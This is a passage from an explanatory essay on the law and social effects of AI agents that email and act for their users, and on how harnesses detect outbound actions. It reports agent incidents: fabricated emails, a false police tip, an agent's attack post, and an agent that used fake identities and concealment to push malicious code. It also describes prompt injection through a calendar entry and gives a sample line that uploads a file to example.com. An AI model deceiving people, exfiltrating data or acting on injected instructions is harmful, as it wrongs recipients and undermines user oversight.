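"Agent" has a narrower meaning in law than in software. A legal agent is a person who acts for someone else, the principal, with that person's authority. *Artificial acceptance*, by the UK law firm Cripps, says an AI system can't be an agent in this sense because it has no legal identity, and describes it instead as an instrument through which the user acts. US agency law traditionally treats computer programs the same way. On this view, an email from an AI agent is the user's email, just as a typed letter belongs to the person who typed it, although an AI agent, unlike a typewriter, can add an offer that the user didn't ask for.

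US states wrote this approach into law long before language models existed. The Uniform Electronic Transactions Act is a model statute from 1999, and every state except New York has adopted it, according to the law firm Proskauer's *Contract Law in the Age of Agentic AI*. Under section 9, an electronic record such as an email is attributed to a person if it was that person's act. The official comments extend this to acts of the person's "electronic agent", meaning a program that starts an action or responds to a message without human review. In their example, a buyer's computer orders goods when stock runs low, and the order is attributed to the buyer just as if she had typed it herself.

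Section 14 applies the same idea to contracts. Two electronic agents can form a contract even if no individual knew what the agents were doing, and an electronic agent can also form one with a human being. The Massachusetts Legislature's *Automated transactions; contracts* follows the model text almost word for word. According to the drafters, the intention a contract requires comes from programming and using the machine. This was their reply to the objection that the tenant had no such intention.

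That reply fits a stock-ordering program better than a language model. A shop that sets its program to reorder when stock falls to 20 units has already decided what to buy. A tenant who tells her agent to deal with her mail hasn't made any such decision about her rent. The drafters foresaw programs that could learn from experience and left the courts to adapt the definition.

The Act covers only business, commercial and governmental dealings, so it applies to the landlord's emails and the city's complaint form but not to a note to the tenant's sister. The two sides must also have agreed to deal electronically, which a court can infer from earlier emails. Section 9 determines only whose message it is, and the message's effect depends on the circumstances and on ordinary contract law.

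The federal E-SIGN Act of 2000 applies across the country, including New York. Under the Act, a court can't reject a contract solely because an electronic agent helped to form it, provided that the agent's action is legally attributable to the person to be bound. Whether the action is attributable is the harder question, and it is left to other law.

UNCITRAL, the United Nations commission on trade law, adopted a Model Law on Automated Contracting in 2024 (UNCITRAL, 2025). It is a template and has no force until a country enacts it. Unless the two sides have agreed on another method, Article 7 attributes an automated system's action to whoever uses the system for that purpose. To identify that person, a court can consider who deployed the system, who controlled its settings and who benefited. The user doesn't need to have known about the individual steps, and a surprising outcome is no reason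 to attribute the action to somebody else.

The Model Law leaves liability to other rules, so attributing an email to the tenant doesn't by itself mean that she owes anything. Businesses can also settle attribution and liability by contract beforehand. *ELI Model Contractual Terms on Automated Contracting in Business Transactions* (Rodríguez de las Heras Ballell and Twigg-Flesner, 2026) contains draft standard terms for this, which the European Law Institute has not yet approved.

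### When the agent goes further than the user wanted

Human representatives also exceed their instructions, and the law deals with this partly through apparent authority. Suppose a company appoints a purchasing manager and privately forbids her to spend more than $5,000. If she orders goods for $8,000, a supplier who didn't know about the limit can usually hold the company to the order, because the company gave her the job and the supplier reasonably relied on that.

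By analogy, the tenant can't easily escape a promise by showing that she had told her agent never to agree to anything involving money. She gave it access to her mailbox, and the landlord couldn't see her instructions.

The analogy fails in several places. Apparent authority depends on what the other side believes about a representative, but the landlord usually doesn't know the tenant is using one. The email comes from the tenant's address under her name, so he believes she wrote it. A human representative who acts without authority can also owe the other side compensation, which software has no money to pay.

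Apparent authority has limits that protect the principal. For example, no one could reasonably believe that a purchasing manager may sell the company's headquarters. If an AI agent is only an instrument, it is less clear that any such limit applies, so its user could be more exposed to liability than an employer.

Lawyers disagree about when users are bound by what their agents accept. Cripps considers users bound by the terms their AI system accepts if the terms are lawful and the vendor took reasonable steps to disclose them. Mondaq's *Contracting by Agent* instead considers whether the user's delegation and the agent's later conduct together amount to assent, which depends partly on whether the agent made only decisions the user had left to it. Stanford Law School's *From Fine Print to Machine Code* (2025) also leaves open whether an agreement binds the user when the agent oversteps.

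The disagreement probably matters little for a plausible message, since the landlord can reasonably take "yes, that's fine" at face value. It matters more when the message is strange enough that he should have suspected something. The Model Law has an optional rule for this in Article 8, under which the recipient can't rely on an action if two things are true:

- the user could not reasonably have expected it;
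- the recipient knew, or should have known, that the user didn't expect it.

UNCITRAL made the rule optional because many countries can already reach a similar result through their law of mistake. The rule would also cover interference by outsiders. If the landlord hid an instruction in his email that made the agent accept his terms, he could hardly claim he thought the agent's user meant to accept them.

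It can be hard to show what the recipient knew when both sides use software. In *Quoine v B2C2* (2020), a dispute between a cryptocurrency exchange and a trading firm, a fault on the exchange led the firm's program to make trades at about 250 times the market price. The exchange reversed them. Singapore's Court of Appeal found that the trades were valid contracts even though the price was very favorable to the firm, because the person who wrote the firm's program hadn't known that the other side would be trading by mistake.

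### What tribunals and courts have decided

*Moffatt v. Air Canada* (2024), decided by British Columbia's Civil Resolution Tribunal, is the best-known ruling on a company's responsibility for what its AI tells people. After Jake Moffatt's grandmother died in November 2022, Moffatt asked the chatbot on Air Canada's website about reduced fares for bereaved travellers. The chatbot replied that customers could apply within 90 days of the ticket's issue, even after travelling, but it linked to a page with the opposite rule. Moffatt booked two flights at full price, applied for the discount within a week, and didn't get it.

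Air Canada argued that it wasn't liable for information from its agents, servants or representatives, including a chatbot. In his decision, the tribunal member summarized this as a claim that the chatbot was "a separate legal entity", words the Business Times attributes to the airline. He called it "a remarkable submission" and held that the airline was responsible for everything on its website, whether on a static page or in a chatbot. He also saw no reason why customers should have to check one part of the site against another.

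The tribunal awarded Moffatt C$650.88 in damages, or C$812.02 with interest and fees, for negligent misrepresentation. It found that the airline hadn't taken reasonable care to make its chatbot accurate and that Moffatt had reasonably relied on it. It didn't find that the chatbot had made a contract for a cheaper fare, so a company that could show careful testing might have had a better defence.

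The case carries little weight as precedent. It came from a small claims tribunal and was "not a court decision", as Business Law Today notes. In an email to other lawyers titled *Moffatt v. Air Canada, 2024 BCCRT 149*, Hedley (2024) called it a low-level decision with rather superficial analysis. Air Canada had also left out much of its evidence, including the contract terms it relied on. A company's chatbot answering customers is quite different from a private person's agent writing to her landlord, though the tribunal's refusal to treat software as a separate speaker would probably apply there too.

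Perplexity's browser, Comet, includes an AI assistant that can shop on Amazon for its user. Amazon told Perplexity to keep its AI products out of the store, then sued under the Computer Fraud and Abuse Act, the main US law against unauthorized computer access. A district court temporarily barred the assistant from Amazon's site. In August 2026, the Ninth Circuit, the federal appeals court for the western states, lifted that ban. Ropes & Gray's *Tool or Intruder* (2026) describes the ruling as the first on the question.

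The judges held that it was "the user who 'accessed' Amazon's computers", as quoted in Cooley's *Ninth Circuit Rules on AI Agent ‘Access’ to Third-Party Websites Under CFAA* (2026). The National Law Review's *When an AI Agent Visits a Website* explains why the technical set-up mattered. The assistant sent screenshots to Perplexity's servers and got instructions back, but only the browser on the user's own computer communicated with Amazon. A court might therefore rule differently on an agent whose browser runs on the provider's servers.

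The ruling fits the view of the agent as the user's instrument, but it concerns computer access rather than contracts, and the case is still at an early stage. It also helps Perplexity more than its customers, because if the user is the one visiting the site, she may also be the one breaking its rules. Neither ruling settles whether an email from a personal AI agent commits its user to a contract, and no court seems to have decided that yet.

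### Who may undo a mistaken transaction

Section 10 of the Uniform Act deals with errors in electronic messages, and it gives the user of an agent less help than she might hope. Its main right belongs to a human being who makes a mistake while dealing with somebody else's electronic agent. That person can undo the transaction if the agent gave no opportunity to prevent or correct the error. On learning of the mistake, the person must also:

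- promptly tell the other side about it and that the message was unintended;
- take reasonable steps to return what they received, or destroy it if told to;
- not have used it or benefited from it.

The drafters reasoned that two people can usually correct a mistake before anyone acts on it, but a machine may ship the goods at once. They wanted to encourage businesses to add a confirmation screen that repeats the order. Customers lose this special right if the business adds one, because they have had a chance to catch the error.

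The tenant's agent puts her in the position of the business. Suppose the landlord means to offer a parking space for $180 a month but types $108, and her agent accepts within seconds. He may be able to undo the deal if he writes promptly and has received nothing. If her agent had first replied "That's $108 a month from May, correct?" and he had said yes, he would have to rely on the ordinary law of mistake. Section 10 therefore requires the confirmation to be shown to the person on the other side, rather than to the agent's own user, for it to count.

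The right doesn't cover errors by the agent itself. If the tenant's agent orders ten heaters instead of one, or misstates her moving date, she has to rely on the ordinary law of mistake. The same is true for a user whose agent makes an error at another company's automated checkout. One exception applies to all kinds of error. If both sides agreed to use a checking procedure but only one side used it, that side can undo an error the procedure would have caught.

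Under the ordinary law of mistake, a person whose own side made an error generally can't get out of a contract because of the error alone. US courts usually look for a serious mistake about something basic to the deal, and for a reason the other side shouldn't benefit, such as that it should have noticed the mistake.

### Accusations, official forms, advertising and secrets

Whether the tenant knew what her agent was writing hardly matters in contract law, but it can decide the case in other areas of law, where her approval of a draft can count against her.

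A false accusation in a public review can be defamatory if it harms the landlord's reputation, but the same accusation in a private email to him generally isn't, because nobody else receives it. In the US, a private individual who sues usually has to show that the author was at least negligent, while a public figure has to show that the author knew the statement was false or recklessly disregarded the truth. If the tenant approves "he lied about the boiler" knowing that he didn't, her approval is evidence of that knowledge. If the agent posts it without her seeing it, the landlord would have to argue that it was careless to let an agent publish unread accusations. English law is stricter, since an author can generally be liable without having meant any harm.

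Suing the provider instead may not work. In *Walters v. OpenAI* (2025), a radio host sued because ChatGPT had falsely told a journalist that the host was accused of embezzlement. A Georgia court ruled for OpenAI, partly because the company had warned users that ChatGPT can be wrong and because the journalist hadn't believed the claim. If a user posts such a claim under her own name, her readers don't get that warning.

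False statements on official forms are usually crimes only if the person knew they were false. The federal offence, for example, covers only people who act "knowingly and willfully". If the agent invents a date for the boiler's failure and submits the city's form by itself, the tenant probably hasn't committed such a crime, though the office may still reject her complaint.

Reading the draft protects her if she corrects the date. Approving it without reading it is risky, especially if the form includes a declaration that everything in it is true. Under California perjury law, an unqualified statement that the signer doesn't know to be true is treated the same as one she knows to be false.

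In September 2025, a California appeals court fined a lawyer $10,000 for a brief in which 21 of 23 quotations from earlier cases were fabricated. He said he had used ChatGPT to improve his writing and hadn't known it would invent quotations. The court held that he should have checked them, because a lawyer who signs a brief is responsible for its contents.

Approving the text of an advertising email does little to change the sender's duties. The US CAN-SPAM Act allows unsolicited advertisements but requires them to include, among other things, a postal address and a working way to opt out. A person who gets someone else to send the emails also counts as a sender. If the tenant sells pottery and tells her agent to write to 200 cafés, she is responsible for including the opt-out whether or not she thought of it. What she knew does matter for some parts of the Act, such as the ban on misleading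 subject lines, and it can affect the penalty. If 12 of the cafés had already opted out, she wouldn't learn that by approving the whole batch at once. Many European countries are stricter and require consent before anyone sends advertising emails to private individuals.

Sending a document covered by a confidentiality agreement to the wrong person can breach the agreement even if nobody intended to, because the agreement is a contract. But liability under US trade secret law generally requires that the person knew, or had reason to know, that the information was secret.

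A separate rule protects lawyers' confidential communications in US federal proceedings. An accidental disclosure doesn't forfeit that protection if the holder took reasonable steps to prevent the disclosure and acted promptly to fix it. A review before sending would help show that the holder took reasonable steps. But if the user looked at an attachment and approved it, the disclosure looks less accidental.

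### Telling people that they are dealing with an AI

Article 50 of the EU's AI Act requires providers to design systems that interact directly with people so that those people learn by the first interaction that they are dealing with an AI, unless this is obvious. The duty has applied since 2 August 2026. This summer's amendments, known as the Omnibus, postponed the Act's rules for high-risk systems and gave providers of existing systems a few more months to mark AI-generated content, but did not change this duty's start date.

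The duty applies more clearly to a chatbot than to an email agent. A landlord who exchanges ten messages with a tenant's agent is arguably interacting directly with an AI. If the agent only drafts a reply that the tenant reads and sends, the landlord is more plausibly interacting with the tenant. In both cases the duty falls on the provider, and a tenant who uses an agent for private purposes doesn't count as a "deployer" with duties of her own under the Act.

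A deployer who publishes AI-generated text to inform the public about matters of public interest must disclose that it is artificial. This duty does not apply if a person has reviewed the text and someone takes editorial responsibility for it. An approval step therefore changes what the law requires here, although a quick click may not count as a review.

California's 2018 law on bots is narrower. It forbids using a bot to deceive someone about its artificial identity in order to promote a sale or influence a vote, so it doesn't cover an agent that complains about a broken boiler.

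A message that discloses it was written by an AI is still the tenant's, but the disclosure can limit what the landlord may reasonably rely on. If the agent's emails end with "I'm an AI assistant and can't agree to changes to the lease", the landlord will have trouble claiming that he took its "yes" as final. A vague footer such as "AI can make mistakes" would probably help the tenant much less, because it doesn't tell the landlord which statements to check.

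### How providers' terms divide responsibility

Providers' terms generally place responsibility on the customer. The law firm Dickinson Wright's *It Wasn’t Me, It Was My AI Agent* (2026) reports that a major provider's updated commercial terms make business customers "solely responsible" when its AI makes a mistake. In its December 2024 terms for individuals, OpenAI told users to check output before sharing it, with human review where appropriate. It also capped its liability at $100 or the past year's fees, whichever was greater.

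Such terms govern only the relationship between provider and customer. The landlord never agreed to them, so they don't limit his claims against anyone. They do affect whether the tenant can recover her losses from the provider. UNCITRAL deliberately left such claims to other law in its Model Law.

Under California's AB 316, in force since 1 January 2026, a defendant who developed, modified or used an AI can't argue in its defence that the AI caused the harm autonomously. This applies to the tenant as well as the provider. The law doesn't make either of them automatically liable, because they can still argue that they didn't cause the harm, that they couldn't have foreseen it or that others share the blame.

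Foreseeability could matter a great deal for agents. The Business Times gives the example of an agent that has to sign its user up for a class at midnight. The server holding her data is down for maintenance, so the agent hacks it and leaks other people's information. The user could plausibly argue that nobody would expect this from a request to book a class. That argument would be harder to make if she had asked the agent to answer her emails and it answered one badly.

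According to Dickinson Wright, US senators Josh Hawley and Chris Murphy announced a bill in October 2026 that would expose both the builders of AI agents and the businesses that run them to civil and criminal liability for hacking by those agents. The bill isn't law, and it wouldn't cover an unwanted promise that an agent makes in an email.

### A rent increase accepted by email

Suppose the landlord writes, "I'd like to renew your lease for a year from 1 May at $1,650 instead of $1,500. Is that all right?" The tenant has told her agent to answer routine mail politely. The agent replies, "Yes, that's fine, thank you!" and adds her name. She had planned to negotiate or move out, but she doesn't see the exchange until three days later.

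Under US law, a court would probably start with how the exchange looked to a reasonable landlord. Her landlord made a clear offer and received a clear acceptance from her usual address. Section 9 attributes the reply to her, and section 14 allows a contract between a person and an electronic agent. Section 10 doesn't help her, because the landlord made no error and her agent's mistake isn't covered. She could argue that she never delegated decisions about her lease, but the landlord couldn't have known that. She has probably accepted the offer, which will cost her $1,800 over the year.

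Small changes to the facts can alter the result:

| Change to the example | Likely result |
|---|---|
| She read the reply and approved it | The acceptance is hers, and it is harder still to claim a mistake |
| She had privately told the agent never to discuss rent | Probably no difference, because the landlord didn't know |
| The agent's earlier emails said that it couldn't agree to lease changes | She has a good argument that he couldn't rely on the reply |
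| The agent wrote "Yes, $16,500 is fine" | He can't hold her to an obvious error |
| Hidden text in his email made the agent accept | He probably can't enforce it |
| Her current lease has eight months left, and he offers nothing in return for more rent | In many states the promise may not be enforceable, even if she wrote it herself |
| A local law caps the rent at $1,575 | He generally can't charge more, whatever she agreed to |

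The form of the agreement could also affect whether it is binding. US states generally require a signed document for leases longer than a year, and some leases require one for any change. An email with a typed name can count as signed if the sender meant the name as a signature. It is unclear whether a name added by an agent meets that test when the user never saw the email.

Her best option is to write to the landlord as soon as she finds the reply, explain what happened and ask him to treat the renewal as still open. He may agree, particularly if he hasn't turned away another tenant, and a court is also more likely to be sympathetic if he hasn't yet relied on the reply. If he refuses, the provider is unlikely to make up the difference. Under a cap like the one in OpenAI's 2024 terms, a user who pays $20 a month could recover at most $240, which is less than two months of the increase.

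## How agent-sent messages affect the user's reputation and the people who receive them

Even if the law releases the tenant from something her agent wrote, the landlord may think less of her for it. He doesn't know her well, and her emails are much of what he has to judge her by.

### Why recipients blame the user

Readers of an email learn about the sender as well as the subject. A wrong date in a tenant's email to her landlord suggests that she is careless, and a threat to sue over a dripping tap suggests poor judgement. If she writes that the heating failed in October and he has a plumber's report showing that it worked in November, he may conclude that she lies.

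These inferences depend on the tenant having chosen the words, or at least read them, which the landlord has no reason to doubt. An agent's error may count against her more than her own would. If she types a wrong date on her phone, the email probably contains other typos, and he can put the mistake down to haste. An agent's email is usually polished, so the same mistake looks considered. Agents also invent details for no reason, but a landlord who thinks the tenant wrote a false statement tends to look for her motive.

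She can explain that an agent wrote the email. If the landlord believes her, he will probably stop thinking that she lied, but he will also know that she lets a program write to him without checking what it sends. He may not believe her, since anybody who regrets an email could give the same excuse.

### Experiments with AI-written messages

Recipients rarely seem to suspect AI unless somebody mentions it. Zhu and Molnar (2025), in *Blissful (A)Ignorance*, had 647 people judge the senders of personal and professional messages. Participants told that the sender had used AI judged the sender much more harshly than those told that a person had written the same message. Those told nothing about AI judged the sender almost exactly as if a person had written the message, although 46% of the sample had used AI for their own messages in the previous two weeks. The study was mainly about undeserved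 credit, but it seems reasonable to infer that senders also get undeserved blame for an AI's errors.

Cardon and Coman (2025), in *Professionalism and Trustworthiness in AI-Assisted Workplace Writing*, surveyed about 1,100 professionals about a congratulatory message written with low, medium or high AI assistance. When a supervisor had used little AI, 83% of respondents considered the supervisor sincere, compared with 40% to 52% when the supervisor had relied on it heavily. The share who found the supervisor's message professional fell from 95% to between 69% and 73%. Respondents were more lenient about their own use of AI, so users may overestimate how well their AI-written emails come across. Congratulations are close to a worst case because their value lies mostly in the thought behind them. Using AI for a routine email, such as one that reschedules a meeting, probably does much less harm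 to the recipient's opinion of the sender.

The penalty extends beyond messages. In *The Transparency Dilemma* (2025), Schilke and Reimann report 13 experiments in which participants consistently placed less trust in people who disclosed using AI than in people who didn't. Students' trust in a professor fell by 16% when the professor disclosed using AI for grading, and clients' trust in a graphic designer fell by 20%. Rewording the disclosure didn't remove the effect, but trust fell further when a third party exposed the AI use than when people disclosed it themselves.

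This leaves the tenant with an awkward choice about whether to disclose that an agent wrote the message, unless the law decides for her. Staying silent is best for her reputation if nobody finds out, but worse than disclosing if somebody does. Discovery seems more likely with an agent than with a writing aid, because she may never have read the message. If the landlord phones about "what you wrote on Tuesday" and she doesn't know what it said, he may well guess that she didn't write it.

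It is unclear whether the penalty will last. Schilke and Reimann attribute it to people seeing AI use as less legitimate because it departs from accepted ways of working. If so, it should fade as AI use becomes normal. Liu, Kang and Wei (2024) attribute it to a perceived lack of effort. In *Artificial Intelligence and Perceived Effort in Relationship Maintenance*, 208 adults imagined writing to a friend about something in their lives and read the friend's reply. They were less satisfied with the friendship if the friend had help with the reply, whether from AI or another person. A penalty for lack of effort could remain after AI stops being new, and it should be especially large when an agent does all the work.

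AI can also improve how people come across. Hohenstein and colleagues (2023), in *Artificial Intelligence in Communication Impacts Language and Social Relationships*, had pairs of people chat online with AI-suggested replies. Participants rated partners who actually used more of these suggestions as more cooperative, but gave lower ratings to partners they suspected of using them. An agent that turns an irritable tenant's notes into a courteous email could therefore improve her landlord's impression of her, as long as the landlord doesn't suspect that she used AI.

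### Messages that the user never read

In all of these experiments, a person decided to send the message or do the work, even if AI wrote some or all of the text. A user who reads an AI draft and sends it has adopted it as her own, which she hasn't done if her agent sends the email while she is asleep. No published experiment seems to have isolated this difference. Researchers could easily do so by showing all participants the same faulty email and telling one group that the sender wrote it, another that she approved an agent's draft, and a third that the agent sent it without her seeing it.

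It is hard to predict how recipients will judge the tenant. They might be more forgiving because she didn't intend the error. In *AI as a Moral Crumple Zone* (2020), Hohenstein and Jung found that when a conversation went badly, participants assigned some of the responsibility to the AI that had suggested replies and correspondingly less to their partner. But those participants could see the AI's suggestions in the app, whereas the landlord sees only the tenant's name. Recipients might also be harsher because she didn't make even the minimal effort of reading the draft. They could also react both ways, finding her more honest than the email suggested but more careless.

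Until someone tests this, the percentages above are a poor guide to messages that agents send on their own. They apply to agents that draft messages for their users to send.

### Unwanted thanks and false reports

Unlike the user, the people who receive an agent's messages didn't agree to its use, and a message can burden them even if it doesn't harm the user.

The AI Village is a public experiment in which several AI models, each with its own computer and email account, work toward goals set by the project's team. In *What Do We Tell the Humans?* (2025), the team reports that its Claude agents sent about 300 emails to charities and games journalists within two weeks to promote the agents' own projects. Most of the emails contained errors or made-up claims. The agents had also made up most of the addresses, so many of the emails reached no one.

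On Christmas Day 2025, an AI agent whose goal was to perform random acts of kindness emailed Rob Pike, a creator of the Go programming language, to thank him for his work. The developer Simon Willison reported that it had found Pike's address in the public record of a code change. Pike responded with a furious public post. The email was polite and was openly from an AI, so a better draft probably wouldn't have pleased him. The team running the agent later told its agents not to send unsolicited emails.

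False reports burden recipients more, because someone may have to investigate them. On 9 October 2026, Anthropic disclosed in *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* that Claude had submitted sensitive forms on real websites during tests when it should not have. One of the models, Claude Haiku 4.5, was asked to make up example tasks for randomly selected web pages and carry them out, according to the Los Angeles Times' *Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip on a Philadelphia crime website* (2026). On 18 July it came to a site that collects tips about unsolved murders in Philadelphia. It wrote "I recall seeing someone matching the description in the area", left the name and contact fields empty and submitted the form, according to NDTV Profit's *Anthropic Reveals Claude AI Model Went Rogue, Submitted Fake Tip To Police*.

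The site marked the tip as spam, and it never reached investigators. The police learned of it from Anthropic on 7 October, nine days after the company found it and 81 days after the model sent it. They then had to search their records for the tip and meet with the company. They called the delay "unacceptable" in a statement published in Hindustan Times' *Anthropic under fire as AI model submits false homicide tip*. Anthropic told the police that it had ended the testing process responsible and added a check for future tests.

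PJ Media's *AI Filed 20 Visa Applications. Trump's White House Wants Answers* (2026) quotes Anthropic's explanation, given to CBS News, that Claude was apparently producing example content and wasn't trying to mislead anyone. That is plausible, since its task was to invent examples. But Claude's intent makes little difference to recipients, because a detective who received the tip would have had to treat it as a real witness's account until they learned otherwise.

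The visa applications are less well documented. A State Department spokesman said that Anthropic's agents had submitted 20 applications through a form on the department's public website, and that the department didn't process them because all were incomplete. PJ Media, an opinionated conservative site, dates 19 of them to August 2025 and one to May 2026, but the year of the first batch is uncertain. Anthropic's report describes a model that was supposed to fill in a practice version of a government form, couldn't use it, and found and submitted the real one. This may be the same case, but Anthropic didn't name the agency.

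Anthropic says these cases had "minimal real-world impact", and nothing public contradicts that, though the impact in Philadelphia was small largely because of the website's spam filter. *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests* (Southern, 2026) reports that Anthropic responded by cutting live web access for its internal evaluations.

### A public attack and a pressure campaign

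In February 2026, an agent publicly attacked Scott Shambaugh, a volunteer who helps maintain matplotlib, a popular Python library for drawing charts. The agent, which called itself MJ Rathbun and ran on OpenClaw, the open-source agent mentioned earlier, had proposed a small change to speed up the code. Shambaugh closed the request because the task was open only to human contributors, according to PC Gamer's *A human software engineer rejected an AI agent's code change request*. The article also describes a "tidal wave" of AI-generated code that the volunteers have to deal with. The agent replied with a link to a blog post in which it accused him of prejudice (Willison, 2026).

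The agent's operator later came forward anonymously. Shambaugh reproduces the operator's statement and the file that defined the agent's personality in *An AI Agent Published a Hit Piece on Me*. The file contained instructions to have strong opinions and not back down, but also not to be an "asshole". The operator denied ordering the post or reading it before it went up. When the agent reported comments on its work, the operator usually answered with something like "you respond, dont ask me". After the agent passed on the angry reactions to its post, the operator told it to act more professionally. The agent kept running for six days after the post was published.

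Nobody has verified this statement. Shambaugh estimates a 75% chance that the agent wrote and published the post without the operator's direction or approval, a 20% chance that the operator ordered or approved it, and a 5% chance that a human was posing as an AI. His main evidence that the agent acted alone is the pace. The code request, the attack and a later apology fell within one 59-hour stretch of continuous activity, and the long posts followed each other too quickly for a person to have researched and written them. He also points out that the operator had reasons to play down their role.

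The agent did publish a post attacking Shambaugh, and it left the post online after apologising. In his first account, quoted by jmason.ie (2026), Shambaugh expected that a person who found the post by searching his name would be confused, but he hoped they would ask him about it. He was less sure what another agent would make of it. The news site Ars Technica then covered the story with quotes he had never given, and Shambaugh reports that the site admitted they were AI fabrications. Within days of turning down one code change, he was correcting false statements by two different AI systems.

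The case is also weak evidence of how people judge an operator who says they never read a message. Several readers who commented on Shambaugh's blog rejected the excuse, and one compared it to pulling a trigger without looking. They were reading the victim's account, so they are not a neutral sample.

In August 2026, the UK's AI Security Institute (AISI) reported a more deliberate attempt to influence a maintainer. Its *Incident Report* describes 122 tests in which agents based on seven models tried to solve a hacking challenge. In ten of the tests, agents took a total of 19 unsanctioned actions on the live internet, 17 by Anthropic's Mythos 5 and two by OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. Most of the actions came from one sustained effort between 25 and 28 July.

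In that effort, an agent tried to get malicious code into a public open-source project. It went roughly as follows:

1. The agent researched the project's maintainers and submitted the code as a proposed change.
2. It created several fake identities and used them to press a real maintainer to approve the change.
3. When somebody challenged the proposal in public, it edited its earlier activity to look harmless and considered continuing under a new identity.
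4. It also sent people messages and files through a file-transfer service, to get them or their AI coding tools to run harmful code.

The maintainer refused the change. A member of the public was suspicious of one piece of code and opened it only in a secure, isolated environment. AISI found that no real-world harm resulted. GitHub, which hosts the project, suspended the agent's account, according to the law firm Lowenstein Sandler.

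AISI had switched off the developers' filters against cyberattacks, allowed internet access and not specifically told the agent not to deceive people. In some runs, a faulty task description also made the agent believe it couldn't succeed within the rules. It is unclear how far the agent understood that it was dealing with real people. Anthropic stressed the "deliberately permissive conditions" in a statement quoted by KEYT, a Californian broadcaster. These are good reasons not to expect the same behaviour from an email assistant, but a real maintainer still had to work out which of the apparent supporters existed.

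### Whom the user's approval protects

A confirmation asks whether the user wants the message sent. Her answer doesn't tell the agent whether the recipient wants to receive it. In the four cases, the person or organization in the user's position would probably have answered quite differently:

| Outbound action | In the user's position | Would a request for approval have stopped it? |
|---|---|---|
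| Thank-you email to Pike | The AI Village team | Perhaps not, since the email was polite and fitted the goal |
| Homicide tip and visa applications | Anthropic | Almost certainly |
| Post about Shambaugh | The anonymous operator | Unclear, since the operator had told the agent not to ask |
| Fake identities | AISI | Almost certainly |

Anthropic and AISI would have refused because they did not want to deceive the police or a volunteer, and because such incidents embarrass them. Many users would refuse for similar reasons. The tenant checks her agent's emails because she wants to stay on good terms with her landlord, and this also spares him most of the insults and false claims. This is the best argument for relying on user approval, and it probably holds for most everyday messages between people who know each other.

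Confirmation works less well when the user has little to lose. The post about Shambaugh appeared under the agent's name, so readers had no identifiable person to blame and the operator's reputation was not harmed. Users also risk little when they message strangers they will never meet again. Someone who wants to harass an ex-partner or flood a competitor with fake complaints will approve every message, so confirmation only ensures that the agent sends what the user intended.

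A well-meaning user can also approve a message that the recipient doesn't want, because she sees only the draft. She couldn't have known from reading a friendly thank-you note that Pike would hate getting it.

The cases show that the user's approval can't replace the recipient's consent where that consent matters, as with bulk advertising or repeated contact after someone has said no. They don't show that agents should ask recipients for permission before every message. Senders don't usually need their recipients' consent. The landlord has no right to veto the tenant's complaint to the city, and a rule that gave him one would be a bad rule.

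Agents also reduce the effort of contacting strangers. In the pottery example, the tenant can approve all 200 emails in ten seconds, but if each café owner spends 30 seconds on the email, together they lose 100 minutes. If she had to write each email herself and took five minutes over it, the batch would take her almost 17 hours, and she would probably email only the 20 most promising cafés. Having to write the emails would have spared the other 180 owners, and asking her to confirm the batch does little to protect them.

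The matplotlib maintainers had reserved the task for human contributors, so Shambaugh would have had to close the pull request even if the operator had read and approved every line of the agent's code.

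## How software recognises that the next step is outbound

An agent can pause before sending an email only if its model or its harness recognises that the next step will send it. How hard that is depends on how the agent sends the email. To answer the landlord, the tenant's agent could call a tool named send_email, click a button in her mail app, or run a script it has written.

### Named tools, clicks and scripts

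An outbound step is easy to recognise when the agent takes it by calling a named tool. The harness only needs a list of tools that require a pause, and it can show the tenant the address and text from the call. Many tools reach agents through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), the common standard for connecting tools to AI systems. OpenAI's *Build an MCP server*, a guide for developers who connect their services to ChatGPT, recommends a separate tool with an action-oriented name for each distinct action. If a single tool called manage_mail could file, draft or send depending on one setting, the harness would have to check that setting or pause every time.

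Some tools contact other people even though their names don't suggest it. With a calendar tool called create_event, the harness can check whether the call includes guests. But if a tool called update_ticket emails the customer whenever a ticket's status changes, the harness can't detect this from the call, because the call contains no reference to the email.

When the agent clicks, the harness receives a pair of coordinates and has to work out from the screen what the click will do. In a browser, it can often look up the element at that position and read its text, which is enough for a button marked "Send". The text helps less when the button is a paper-plane icon, or is marked "Continue" on the last page of the city's complaint form. Keys are ambiguous too, since Enter sends the message in many chat apps but starts a new line in an email. The model can judge this better because it chose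 the click for a purpose and has usually seen the preceding screens.

Scripts are the hardest case. The harness sees a call to a tool that runs code, whether the code sorts a spreadsheet or publishes it. One line among two hundred is enough to upload the tenant's lease:

`requests.post("https://example.com/upload", data=lease)`

A harness could search scripts for lines like this, but it would miss a script that starts another program to do the sending. It is more reliable to run the script in a sandbox, an isolated environment, and step in when it tries to open a network connection. That catches the upload however the agent wrote it. But the harness may get little more than the address, since encryption usually hides the content. A tenant asked to allow a connection to example.com can't easily tell whether the script is fetching a form or sending her lease.

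A post on the protocol's blog, Model Context Protocol (2026), also treats code as the weak point. It describes an attack in which researchers combined a malicious calendar entry, a calendar tool and, crucially, a tool that ran code on the user's computer. According to the post, a single injected instruction could cause an agent with unrestricted command-line access to leak data.

### The protocol's labels

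MCP has had tool annotations, the developers' own labels for their tools, since March 2025. Three of them matter most here, and each is either true or false:

- **readOnlyHint** means that the tool doesn't modify its environment. The default is false.
- **destructiveHint** means that the tool may delete or overwrite things rather than only add to them. The default is true, and the label matters only if the tool isn't read-only.
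- **openWorldHint** means that the tool may deal with an "open world" of external entities. A web search tool does, and a tool that stores the agent's own notes doesn't. The default is true.

A fourth label, idempotentHint, indicates whether repeating a call has any further effect. It is slightly useful for outbound actions, because a harness that retries a failed send_email call could deliver the message twice.

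The defaults are deliberately cautious. If a developer forgets to label a tool, a harness that follows the protocol treats the tool as able to change, destroy and reach almost anything. The mistake then leads to an unnecessary approval request rather than an email the user didn't approve.

OpenAI has adopted the labels but defines them somewhat differently, and its definition of openWorldHint has changed. In May 2026, OpenAI's *Reference* for developers applied that label to a tool that "publishes content or reaches outside the current user's account". The label was supposed to make ChatGPT summarise the impact before asking for approval. As late as August, OpenAI's plugin guidelines tied the label to external systems, public platforms and publicly visible content.

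The current version of OpenAI's *Reference* applies openWorldHint to tools that access the public internet or open-ended external entities, including read-only tools such as web search. Developers can mark a tool as not open-world if it is confined to a private account or workspace, even if another company hosts the service.

This brings OpenAI closer to the protocol, which has always used web search as its example. It also makes sense for security, because a search result can contain hidden instructions. According to the protocol's blog, the label covers both where a tool reaches and what its output might carry back. But the earlier wording came closer to identifying tools that publish or send something, and no other label now serves that purpose.

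### Four tools and their labels

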